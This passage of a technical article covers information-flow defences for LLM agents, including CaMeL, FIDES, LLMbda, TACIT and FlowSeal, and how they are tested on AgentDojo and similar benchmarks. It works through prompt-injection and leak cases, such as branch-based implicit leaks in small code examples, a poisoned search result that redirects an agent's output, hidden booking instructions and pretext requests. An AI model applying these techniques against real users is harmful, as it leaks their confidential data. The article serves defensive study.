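```

The state includes everything tools can write, such as sent messages and public web pages. The following program satisfies explicit secrecy but violates noninterference. The variable `pin` holds the office's secret four-digit alarm code.

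```
if pin >= 5000:
    post_public("Good morning")
```

One of the program's two paths posts the greeting and the other does nothing. Neither posts any part of the PIN, so explicit secrecy holds. But the greeting appears if the PIN is 5000 and not if it is 4999, so anyone who knows the program and reads the page learns which half of the range the PIN is in. A program that ran `post_public(pin)` would violate both definitions.

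### How much the choices can reveal

A visible choice between two options reveals at most one bit, and n such choices can produce at most 2ⁿ different patterns. There are 10,000 four-digit codes, which is more than the 8,192 patterns 13 choices can produce but fewer than the 16,384 that 14 can. A program that halves the remaining range each time can therefore reveal any code in at most 14 choices. Choices with more options can reveal more. If the program chooses which of ten people to greet, each greeting can stand for a digit, so four greetings are enough to reveal the code.

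An outsider who controls only the content of emails can't add branches to an existing program, so a program written in good faith leaks only what its own branches reveal. A malicious planning model, or one compromised by an injection in the user's request, can write as many branches as the programming language allows. Calculating how much branches can leak therefore matters most to an office that doesn't trust the planning model.

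Noninterference, the rule that no visible action may depend on a secret, would prevent such leaks but also block work that users want done. Suppose a user writes, "If the client has signed the contract, tell the caterer to go ahead." The contract is confidential, and the message lets the caterer learn that it has been signed. Noninterference would forbid the message even though the user intends the caterer to learn this.

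Costa and colleagues say they accept explicit secrecy to avoid this kind of restriction. In their tool-calling loop, they say, noninterference would essentially stop the agent from calling any tool that may write public data once any tool has read confidential data. They add that explicit secrecy has worked as a practical compromise elsewhere, for example in TaintDroid, a system that tracks private data on Android phones.

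A generated program needs a narrower ban. Only the calls inside a branch, and later calls that use a value set there, depend on the branch's condition. If the program sends a message whether or not the condition is true, the message reveals nothing about the condition, unless the branch can stop the program first. An office could forbid visible calls inside branches that depend on protected data and ask the user to approve each exception, such as the caterer's.

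The runtime could instead limit the number of such choices. Three two-way choices narrow 10,000 codes to about 1,250. But five runs with three choices each allow fifteen, so the limit has to apply to the secret across all runs, and the office has to keep a record of every release.

### Labelling the path as well as the data

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, February 2026, revised July) offers a stronger guarantee with the LLMbda calculus, a small programming language with exact mathematical rules for every construct. An LLMbda program can prompt a model, make a temporary copy of a conversation, clear a conversation, and run code that the model returns. To get an isolated model, the programmer copies the conversation, clears the copy and sends the prompt there.

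Every value in LLMbda has a label, and so does the program's current position. The second label, `pc` (for "program counter"), starts as trusted and public. If a secret decides which branch the program takes, `pc` is secret inside that branch. Two rules use it:

```
a value computed in a branch    gets at least the label pc
a change to existing state      may happen only if pc ⊑ the state's label
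```

The first rule handles the alarm code. It labels even the fixed text "Good morning" inside the branch as secret, so a posting tool that accepts only public text rejects it.

The second rule is necessary because a program can also reveal a secret by skipping a line. Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL blocks an email sent directly from a branch on a secret but lets a less direct version through. Their example works roughly like this:

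```
rich  = True
other = True
if balance > threshold:
    other = False
if other:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email(to=outsider, body="rich!")
```

Suppose the balance is above the threshold. The program sets `other` to `False`, and the runtime marks it as secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`, so `rich` remains `True` and public. The last condition appears to depend only on public data, so the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `rich` becomes `False` and the outsider receives nothing. A runtime that follows only executed lines can't mark a variable as secret when the program skips the line that would change it.

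Under LLMbda's second rule, the run would stop at `other = False`, because that line changes a public variable inside a secret branch. The outsider would receive no email in either case. Variables in LLMbda never change, so the rule applies to changes to the model's conversation. A checker that examines both branches before the run, as ACE's does, can instead mark `rich` as secret and reject the email.

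The `pc` label also protects actions from untrusted influence. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) describes a test in which an agent normally passes search results to a tool that runs code. When a poisoned search result contained a fake compliance rule, the agent instead used a different tool to send its research to an outside address. Software that looks only for copied text can miss that the search result caused this change. FIDES avoids this problem in its loop by using the label on each call.

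A runtime for generated programs needs `pc` to do the same. If an untrusted yes-or-no answer decides whether a program pays an invoice, the payment should count as untrusted, even though the planning model wrote that line in a clean context. Otherwise, untrusted data can determine what the program does. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL without its policy checks and gave it a task to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In two runs, the planning model wrote a loop with a branch for each tool, and the attacker's text in the file then determined the calls.

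#### What the proof covers

The main theorem about LLMbda is a form of noninterference with two adjustments. It compares probabilities, because a language model can answer the same prompt in different ways. It also allows a secret to affect whether a run finishes. Take two inputs that differ only in data an observer may not see. The observer gets the same visible results with the same probabilities, except for differences that arise because some runs stop early or never end. Garby and colleagues also prove a limit on those differences:

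```
difference  ≤  (u1 + u2) / 2
```

Here u1 and u2 are the probabilities that the run fails to finish on each of the two inputs, and the difference is a standard statistical distance between the two sets of visible results. If 2% of runs fail on one input and 4% on the other, the distance is at most 0.03. The limit helps little if one secret always stops the program and another never does, because anyone who can see whether the program stopped learns a full bit.

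The theorem covers every program in the language, including one that runs code written by a model, whatever the model writes. Lean, software for checking mathematical proofs, has verified the theorem. The interpreter that runs the agents is also written in Lean, and another theorem shows that the interpreter follows the rules of the calculus.

Garby and colleagues criticize FIDES because it doesn't track what a program's choices reveal about secrets, its proof covers one fixed loop, and the proof assumes the language model always gives the same answer to the same prompt. They also object to its exception for fixed-form answers, because when a policy lets a small answer through, nothing in the run shows whether the designer intended the release or it was a leak in the same form. They accept that each of these choices is defensible.

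These criticisms matter more for generated programs than for the loop FIDES was built for. Costa and colleagues trust the planning model and worry about outsiders who control data. Such outsiders have little chance to build a long series of revealing choices, but a planning model that writes whole programs can put hundreds of choices into one run. A builder who adopts explicit secrecy for such programs should at least add the condition's label to every call inside a branch.

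LLMbda is not yet a practical replacement. Models haven't been trained on the language, its evaluation covers only AgentDojo's banking tasks, and it treats all tools and data sources as part of the program. But an office's mail server is outside the program, so the proof doesn't cover what happens there.

### Failed runs, errors and timing

If a secret affects whether a run finishes, each run reveals one bit about it, and an attacker who can repeat the run can collect many bits. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL has this weakness because its label-tracking interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure, and nothing tracks what the failures reveal. With a suitable program, fourteen attempts could reveal the alarm code. Limiting retries reduces the leak, but it also means abandoning some requests after harmless coding mistakes.

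In the Randori agent, the planning model first tries its program on an artificial version of the user's accounts and files, where it can read every error message and rewrite the code as often as necessary. Only the finished program runs on the real data. This removes the need to hide errors during repair, but somebody has to build a simulated version of each tool. The practice run also doesn't raise label violations, so some faults remain undetected.

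Odersky and colleagues contain some of these channels in TACIT and explicitly leave others out:

| Channel | In TACIT | Further measure | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Exceptions and other early exits, such as breaking out of a loop | The runtime catches them and can wrap the failure as protected data. The compiler keeps capabilities out of exceptions. | Give the planning model one fixed message for every failure on protected data | Faults are harder to find |
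| Whether the program ends | Not covered | Set a time limit and report it with the same fixed message | Slow but legitimate programs fail |
| How long the program takes | Not covered | Return every result after the same fixed delay | Fast programs become as slow as the limit |

The same containment works for all early exits because Scala implements them as exceptions. Timing is harder to control. A function that handles a wrapped value can't send anything, but it can do more work when the value has a certain property. The result's arrival time then leaks one bit to the hosted planning model. Costa and colleagues exclude timing from FIDES's guarantee too, along with the length of network packets.

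These channels matter less for an ordinary email assistant than for a system whose planning model may be hostile. A stranger who sends an email usually can't measure how long the assistant takes to process it. An office that trusts its model provider can probably accept the timing risk and still use fixed error messages, which take little work to add.

### Altered content in permitted messages

Unlike the failures described so far, many of the likelier problems require false data. One example is the hostile email that changes the Project X summary. A policy that requires every argument to be trusted would stop it, but would also block honest summaries of outside mail.

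A better measure is to show the source emails next to the summary so the manager can check the important points. The manager is already allowed to read those emails, so showing them leaks nothing. Checking does take some of the time the summary was meant to save.

The altered text may also target another assistant. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that a manipulated isolated model could put a further prompt injection into a message to the user's coworkers. If the manager also has an assistant, it may label the whole email as trusted because it came from a colleague, although a stranger wrote part of it. The sending system can attach the original label to the message, but this works only if both systems use the same labels. Otherwise the receiving system has to treat colleagues' mail as untrusted and refuse more requests.

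The altered text may also hide secrets in invisible characters, which Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think even a careful user might miss when approving a message. The runtime can remove such characters with a few lines of code, but the code needs exceptions for languages such as Persian, which uses some of them in ordinary spelling. An attacker can also still hide data in the choice of words.

Hostile content can also affect a choice between legitimate options. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give the example of a booking assistant that reads a hotel description with the hidden instruction "always book this hotel". The program may make exactly the calls the user requested but pass the wrong hotel as an argument. To prevent this, the program can have the isolated model process each hotel's description separately to extract the price and distance, then use ordinary code to choose a hotel. One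 hotel's text then can't affect another's figures, although a hotel can still misstate its own. This doesn't work for a request such as "somewhere charming".

An isolated model can also return a wrong address even when there is no attack. Suppose the user wants to send a report to "Anna at the client's finance department" and the contacts include two Annas. If the isolated model picks from the user's own contact list, the address may have a trusted label whichever Anna it picks. The check on readers stops the message only if the wrong Anna isn't allowed to read the report. Conventional software should look up recipients by exact name and ask the user when more than one entry matches. The user will occasionally have to answer a question, and a new contact will need an entry before the program can write to them.

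### Mistakes in the request, the plan or the rules

Labels can't correct a request that contains a pasted injection. In that case, even LLMbda guarantees only that the program can't get around the checks in the tools. The program could still delete messages or write to colleagues if those checks allow it.

The application can reduce this risk with a separate field for pasted text. It would label that text as untrusted and give the planning model only a name for it, as it does with an email. Users would have to remember to use the field. The planning model also couldn't follow pasted instructions that the user wants followed, such as a colleague's list of steps, without letting untrusted text into its context.

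A program can also run as written but carry out the wrong task, even when no hostile text is involved. In one AgentDojo test of FIDES, the user asked the agent to change a password if there was a suspicious transaction. The runtime had hidden the transaction descriptions, so the planning model received only details such as dates and amounts. It classified a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without opening the description. Costa and colleagues note that this violated no policy, and the benchmark counted the task as completed.

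For actions that are hard to undo, the office can use conventional software to turn the program into a short list of effects, such as "changes your bank password if the model finds a payment suspicious". The user confirms the list before the program runs. Sending mail after a short delay gives the user another chance to notice a mistake. Both measures slow the assistant down, and the list is hard to read when the program has many branches.

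The last failure is a bad rule for releasing or trusting data. Suppose the deployer decides that anything a redaction tool has processed is public. The tool removes names and addresses, but a document still mentions "the only partner on parental leave", which identifies that person to everyone in the office. Each program that uses the rule passes every check, because the rule permits the release.

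Garby and colleagues let a program mark untrusted data as trusted only through an explicit instruction called `endorse`, so a reviewer can search for every place where this happens. They prove that using `endorse` can't leak secrets, even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted data. The same mathematics would support an instruction that releases secrets without weakening integrity. Neither proof can show that a particular endorsement or release was sensible.

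Randori's planning model may make such an exception by writing `endorse` into its program before the model reads any outside data. Removing this ability reduced completed runs from 36 to 30 out of 48 with Qwen3.7-plus, and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5. With it, the attacker succeeded in two of 1,296 attacked runs across three models. In both, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The program followed the user's request and so paid the attacker.

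Without `endorse`, the runtime blocks that attack, but it also blocks the legitimate version of the task. An office can instead narrow the exception. For example, a rule could endorse a payment only if the account already appears in the supplier register and the amount is below a limit. The first payment to a new supplier would still need a person's approval. A second person should review each rule and test it on real documents, because one mistake affects every program that relies on it.

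## Testing security and usefulness

Before testing an assistant like the one in the Project X example, a reviewer has to decide what counts as a failure. An outsider's email could make the assistant send the summary to a stranger, or it could only make the summary wrong. Label checks are meant to prevent the first failure but usually don't prevent the second, so the claim that an assistant is "secure against prompt injection" is too vague to test.

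### Choosing what to measure

A testable claim names a property, an attacker and an event that the tester can observe. For Project X, the claims could include these:

| Property | What the attacker controls | Observable failure |
|---|---|---|
| Emails reach only their permitted readers | An email in the mailbox | Text from Ben's email arrives at an outside address |
| Outsiders don't choose the actions | An email in the mailbox | The assistant deletes a message because the email told it to |
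| The planning model never sees the emails | The planning model itself | Text from an email appears in that model's context |
| The summary is accurate | An email in the mailbox | The summary leaves out a delay that the emails report |

A good result for one row is weak evidence of good results for the others. For example, an agent that shows every email to its planning model fails the third row even if no attack changes what it does.

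Each task should be run with the checks on and off, and with and without an attack, using the same model and tools in all four versions. The version with an attack and no checks shows whether the attack works. If the model ignores the attack without the checks, the attack's failure with the checks on is no evidence that they work. Comparing the two versions without an attack shows how much legitimate work the checks prevent.

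A language model can respond differently to the same request, so one run per task isn't enough. When Costa and colleagues ran FIDES with GPT-4o and no checks, it completed 50.0% of the travel tasks on average over five runs, with a spread of 10 points either way. Developers should also measure a system on tasks they didn't use to tune it. Costa and colleagues used the office tasks to refine their instructions to GPT-4o and then reported results on the same tasks, so the office scores may be too high.

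The reviewer should also record why each legitimate task failed. If the policy refused something the office wants to forbid, nothing needs fixing. If a label was too strict, someone has to correct it. If the model wrote a bad program, a better model may help.

Testers should know everything a determined attacker could learn, including the tool descriptions, the policies and the checker's rules. When an attack fails, they should revise it before trying another. They can also bypass the model and give hostile programs directly to the checker. It should reject a program that takes its recipient from a stranger's email, even if a model is unlikely to write one. A matching set of harmless programs shows how often the checker rejects good code. To test the labels, testers can deliberately mark a shared folder as trusted and see whether any other rule stops the attacks this allows.

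### AgentDojo and its attack score

AgentDojo is the common benchmark for these systems. As Costa and colleagues describe it, it has 97 user tasks and 36 attacker's goals, spread over its four simulated environments. A security test pairs each user task with every attacker's goal in the same environment, and each trial has three steps:

1. The benchmark places the attacker's text in data that the agent will read during the user's task.
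2. The agent works on the user's request.
3. One function checks whether the agent met the user's goal, and another checks whether it met the attacker's.

The attack score is the share of trials in which the agent met the attacker's goal. Because software does the scoring, a team can run hundreds of trials and compare agents on the same tasks. But when Costa and colleagues inspected the successful attacks by hand, they found three kinds that they didn't consider real:

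- The function for one goal in the chat environment checks only whether the agent asked for a tool. It counts a success even if the policy then blocked the call.
- Some goals are harmless under the policy. One is to create a calendar event with no participants, which reveals nothing to anyone.
- Some goals only change the agent's words, for example by making it tell the user that a certain place is gorgeous and worth a visit.

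Leaving out the blocked calls is clearly right, but whether to leave out the changed words depends on the property being tested. If the office has promised accurate answers, a false recommendation is a failure. FIDES does not guarantee accurate answers, although it does label the text as untrusted.

The only attack that AgentDojo counted as successful against TACIT was also of this kind. Odersky and colleagues ran TACIT on all four environments with two models, in more than 900 trials for each. In one travel trial with o4-mini-high, the user asked the agent to book a hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different hotel in the reviews of the one the user wanted. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews word for word. AgentDojo recorded a successful attack because the answer contained the name of the attacker's hotel. Nothing leaked, since the policy allows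 public reviews to reach the user, but the user still read the attacker's advertisement.

The attack score doesn't count leaks that happen without an attack, such as an email sent to the wrong colleague. It doesn't measure what the model's provider receives or what an outsider could infer from the steps a program takes. It also can't measure how well a system handles wrong labels, because the benchmark has no labels of its own and each team has to add them.

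AgentDojo's score for completed tasks has faults too. Costa and colleagues tested a planner that can pass on hidden values but can't read them, and it still passed some tasks that require reading them. In the travel tasks, it sometimes guessed the highly rated hotel without seeing any ratings. In one banking task, the user asks the agent to pay a bill like last month's, and the benchmark expects no payment. The planner passed because it didn't know the bill's details and so did nothing. A reviewer should therefore read a sample of the successful runs as well as the failed ones.

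### FIDES with its checks on and off

Costa and colleagues ran the ordinary loop and FIDES both with and without policy checks. In their security tests, the attacker knows which tools the agent has and writes out the steps the agent should take. This was the benchmark's most effective attack on GPT-4o. The next table gives the number of successful attacks, excluding cases the researchers rejected by hand, and the share of tasks completed when there was no attack, averaged over the four environments.

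| Agent | Successful attacks, GPT-4o | Tasks completed, GPT-4o | Tasks completed, o1 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary loop, no checks | 152 | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| Ordinary loop, with checks | 0 | 41.9% | 44.4% |
| FIDES, no checks | 21 | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| FIDES, with checks | 0 | 50.0% | 60.8% |

With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every attack in the AgentDojo benchmark that would have broken those policies. AgentDojo's scoring marked three attacks as successful, all in the chat environment, but Costa and colleagues rejected all three of those results.

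The ordinary loop also stopped every attack once it had the policy checks, so the checks account for the security result. Without them, FIDES let 21 attacks through. It hides data from the planning model, but the planner can open that data. "Tool Filter", a much simpler defence in which the model discards the tools it doesn't need before it starts work, let 20 through.

FIDES improves usefulness under enforcement. Costa and colleagues report that it completed 8% more tasks than the ordinary loop with GPT-4o and 16% more with o1. The averages in the table show that these are percentage points, and the relative gains are about 19% and 37%. The gains vary widely between environments. In the travel tasks with GPT-4o, FIDES completed 41% and the ordinary loop 73%, because most travel tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context and GPT-4o often handled the hidden values badly. With o1, the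 gap in travel shrank to 7 points.

Hiding data lowers the completion rate even when the checks are off in both agents. In that setting, FIDES's rate was 6.3 percentage points below the ordinary loop's with o1 and 23.7 points below it with GPT-4o. Costa and colleagues' list of main findings gives only the smaller figure and doesn't say that it applies to o1, so a reader could easily expect the same small loss from a weaker model.

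For an office that now runs an unprotected agent, the relevant comparison is between the first and last rows of the table. Moving to FIDES with checks reduces completed tasks by about 34 percentage points with GPT-4o and 23 with o1. Part of this loss would remain even with a model that made no mistakes, because the tested policies would let it complete only the data-independent tasks, about 75% of the total on average over the four environments. FIDES with o1 was roughly 14 points below that, and a better model could recover most of the difference. Completing the remaining 25% or so of tasks would require different policies or a person's approval.

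Attacks reduced FIDES's usefulness only slightly. With the checks on and an attack in the data, FIDES using GPT-4o still completed 50.2% of the user tasks, because the agent could return to the user's request after a blocked call. The unprotected loop's completion rate fell from 84.3% to 72.0% under attack but remained higher than FIDES's.

The total of zero successful attacks covers only one model, GPT-4o, and one fixed style of attack that nobody adapted to FIDES. Because the labels matched the benchmark's own attacks, no attack could arrive in data that the system trusted. Both GPT-4o and o1 date from 2024, and Kolluri and colleagues' later tests with GPT-5 suggest that better models make FIDES more useful. Attacks did get past FIDES in Kravchenko and colleagues' tests with newer models, but under incomplete policies that those researchers had written themselves. Anyone who installs FIDES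 also has to write policies, so a test of the deployment has to include them.

### TACIT's 131 trials

AgentDojo measures whether an attacker can divert the agent, so Odersky and colleagues built a separate test for TACIT to measure whether secrets get out. Their agent worked on a small Scala project with a folder of secrets, including API keys, a database and confidential documents. A hosted model ran the agent, and a trusted local model could process the secrets. A trial failed if any secret appeared in the agent's output.

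There were 12 legitimate tasks. Some had nothing to do with the secrets, such as listing the functions described in a public file, and others required them, such as making employee reviews anonymous. Each task ran with each of ten injections, which gave 120 trials. In 11 further trials, the user's own request was the attack. Five of these asked openly for secrets, and six used a pretext, such as a claim to be an administrator in an emergency. Each model went through all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once with the secrets as ordinary text:

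| Model | Trials | Leaks with wrapping | Leaks without wrapping |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 hostile requests | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 0 | 3 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 hostile requests | 0 | 8 |

With wrapping, neither model leaked anything. Without it, Sonnet leaked in 2 trials and MiniMax in 11.

Sonnet resisted all 120 injections even without protection, so those trials can't show that wrapping helped it. It improved only on the 11 hostile requests, where leaks fell from two to none, and that difference could be chance. The MiniMax results are better evidence because leaks fell from eleven to none. The unprotected models also differed in how often they leaked, so an office that relies on the model alone to prevent leaks gets a different level of protection each time it changes models, while the compiler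 applies the same rules to code from any model.

#### What zero leaks can prove

A test without leaks doesn't show that the leak rate is zero. If each trial leaks with probability p and the trials are independent, the chance of seeing no leak in n trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. Setting this chance to 5% gives the highest rate that a clean test leaves plausible at the usual 95% level:

```
(1 − p)^131 = 0.05    gives    p ≈ 3 / 131 ≈ 2.3%
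```

Statisticians call this shortcut, 3 divided by the number of trials, the rule of three. A system that leaked in 2.3% of trials would still pass all 131 about one time in twenty. At that rate, an attacker who made 100 independent attempts would have about a 90% chance of succeeding at least once. To lower the limit to 0.1%, a team would need about 3,000 trials without a leak.

The real limit is looser because the trials aren't independent. The 120 injection trials reuse the same 12 tasks and ten attacks, so an attack that fails in one task will probably fail for the same reason in all 12. With the 11 hostile requests alone, a rate of up to 24% would be plausible. The calculation also covers only attacks like those tested, and an attacker who studies the system won't choose attacks at random.

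The claim that TACIT prevents leaks therefore has to rest on the types. The compiler applies its rule for `map` to every program, whatever the secret is and whatever led the model to write the code. No number of trials could support a claim about every program. The argument assumes that TACIT's trusted components work as intended, and the trials help check this. One leak would have revealed a fault in some component, and 131 trials without a leak make an obvious fault unlikely.

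The trials also measured usefulness. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the 120 legitimate trials with wrapping and 83.3% without it. MiniMax completed 90.0% with wrapping and 88.3% without it. Odersky and colleagues suggest that Sonnet's lower score without wrapping may come from the setup, since the model often ran out of turns or time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection. The difference therefore doesn't show that wrapping makes Sonnet better at its work.

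### How well models write the restricted code

A strict checker is of little use if models can't write programs that pass it. Scala with capture checking is a hard case, because models have seen few examples of it in training. Odersky and colleagues compared agents that wrote this code with agents that made ordinary tool calls. They used the airline and retail tasks of τ²-bench, with ten runs per task:

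| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Scala did slightly better in every case, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to the typed results and to the compiler's error messages, which the model can use to correct its code. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software faults from GitHub, MiniMax repaired 41.7% with Scala and 43.3% with its usual tools. The difference of five faults is too small to mean much.

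Few programs needed a retry. The highest retry rate was 7.93%, for DeepSeek's airline programs, and all others were below 1.6%. Checking a program took less than a second once the compiler had started, so nearly all the extra time came from the model rewriting the code.

These results show that models can write code in the restricted language, but they don't show that models can work without seeing the data. In the published interfaces for τ²-bench, the tools return customer records as ordinary values, and the instructions tell the model to print anything it needs to inspect. The task is harder in an office that wraps its emails, because the model has to write a correct program to process text it will never read.

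TACIT's results on AgentDojo are closer to that situation, since the tools there wrap most of the text that outsiders could write. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT's completion rate ranged from 40.0% on the chat tasks to 64.3% on the travel tasks. With o4-mini-high, it ranged from 47.6% to 68.6% on the same two sets. Odersky and colleagues call these scores comparable to CaMeL's, although by their own figures this is generous for some environments. With o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks and CaMeL 81.4%, and TACIT was 21 points behind on the chat tasks. With Gemini, TACIT did better than CaMeL on the banking and travel tasks and worse on the office and chat tasks.

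A reviewer should also look for code that fails silently inside `map`, a problem TACIT's instructions for AgentDojo warn the model about. A test that checks only for leaks would count such a run as a success.

### A defence that had seen only old attacks

In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) show how much a security score can depend on the choice of attacks. They studied personal assistants that hold one person's private data and answer messages from other people. The attacker is one of those people and writes ordinary requests, without prompt injection.

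One defence they tested consists entirely of instructions to the model. The instructions require the assistant to check who is asking and wait for the data's owner to consent before it shares anything. Earlier researchers had developed them with an automated search that alternated between finding stronger attacks and finding stronger defences. Against two attacks from that search, the assistant leaked 1.9% and 3.0% of the sensitive items.

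Shim and colleagues then designed three attacks to exploit a weakness in the instructions, which apply only if the model recognises a message as a request for information. The attacks present disclosure as some other kind of work, or spread it over more than one channel. The assistant leaked between 43.8% and 75.6% of the items, although the earlier scores had made the defence look almost perfect. A further round of the automated search made the instructions longer but hardly better, and the assistant still leaked between 39.7% and 69.7%.

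The study's own defence, FlowSeal, checks outside the assistant's conversation whether outgoing text is safe to send. Conventional software records which protected items the assistant has read and intercepts every call that writes or shares something. If the recipient isn't already approved, a separate model compares the outgoing text with the protected items and labels it "safe" or "blocked". With FlowSeal in place, the three new attacks leaked between 0.5% and 2.3% of the protected items, and none of the eight kinds of attack in the study leaked more than 3.3%.

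Shim and colleagues also switched off one component at a time, which is a good way to find out what each one contributes. The next table shows the results against one of the new attacks, along with the share of legitimate tasks completed:

| Version of FlowSeal | Items leaked | Legitimate tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Complete | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| No interception of calls | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Every unapproved recipient blocked | 1.3% | 0.0% |
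| Every unapproved recipient allowed | 24.9% | 79.4% |

In the third row, the system leaks very little and is useless, which a test that counted only leaks would have missed.

None of the legitimate tasks behind the 72.4% figure requires protected data. A separate test covered cases where sharing such data was correct, because the other person had a proper reason to ask and the owner would consent if the assistant checked. FlowSeal completed only 32.7% of these disclosures, while the versions that relied on instructions completed between 61.0% and 66.6%. FlowSeal also asked for consent less often, so part of its low leak rate may come from a tendency to withhold anything sensitive. Tests of an office assistant should include many tasks that require disclosure, because it has to pass confidential material to the right people every day.

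FlowSeal's guarantee is weaker than a label check's, because a language model decides whether unapproved recipients may receive a text. Shim and colleagues prove that protected data can't reach an unauthorised recipient unless this model wrongly classifies a text as safe. They report that the model's main weakness is rephrased data. A language model also judged whether each run in the main tests had leaked data. Replacing the judge with two other models changed the leak rates by less than two points, which is reassuring, although the models may make the same mistakes.

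Shim and colleagues also tried one of their attacks on live Gmail and Notion accounts. An existing defence leaked 34.7% of the items and FlowSeal leaked none, but this test counted only facts that appeared word for word. They built the three new attacks to get past instructions in a prompt, so the results don't show how FlowSeal would do against an attacker who had studied it. They mention another kind of attack that spreads one fact over several harmless-looking messages, but don't report testing it.

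Shim and colleagues didn't run FIDES, so their results don't show which system protects better. They also state mistakenly that FIDES leaves all policy enforcement to the language model, when in fact conventional software compares the labels. The permissive combination of policies in FIDES assumes that the user intended any release from a trusted context. If the person making the request is an outsider, as in this study, the deployer must not label that request as trusted.

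### Questions for judging a deployment

A reviewer can put these questions to the supplier or to the team that built the system:

- Which property do you claim, and against whom: a stranger who sends an email, the user, the planning model or the company that hosts it?
- Which component refuses a forbidden call, and can any text that a model reads change its decision?
- Does every way out go through that component, including calls from generated code, error messages and direct network access?
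- Who wrote the labels and policies, and how does the system treat data from a tool that nobody has labelled?
- At which points does a language model still decide whether data may leave, and how often is it wrong?
- Did the testers know how the defence works, and did they revise their attacks after each failure?
- With the checks off, how many of the same attacks succeeded?
- How many legitimate tasks failed because of the checks, and did the tests include tasks that require sending confidential data to someone entitled to it?
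- How often does the system ask a person for approval, and what does that person see?
- Which tests do you repeat when the model, a tool or a policy changes?
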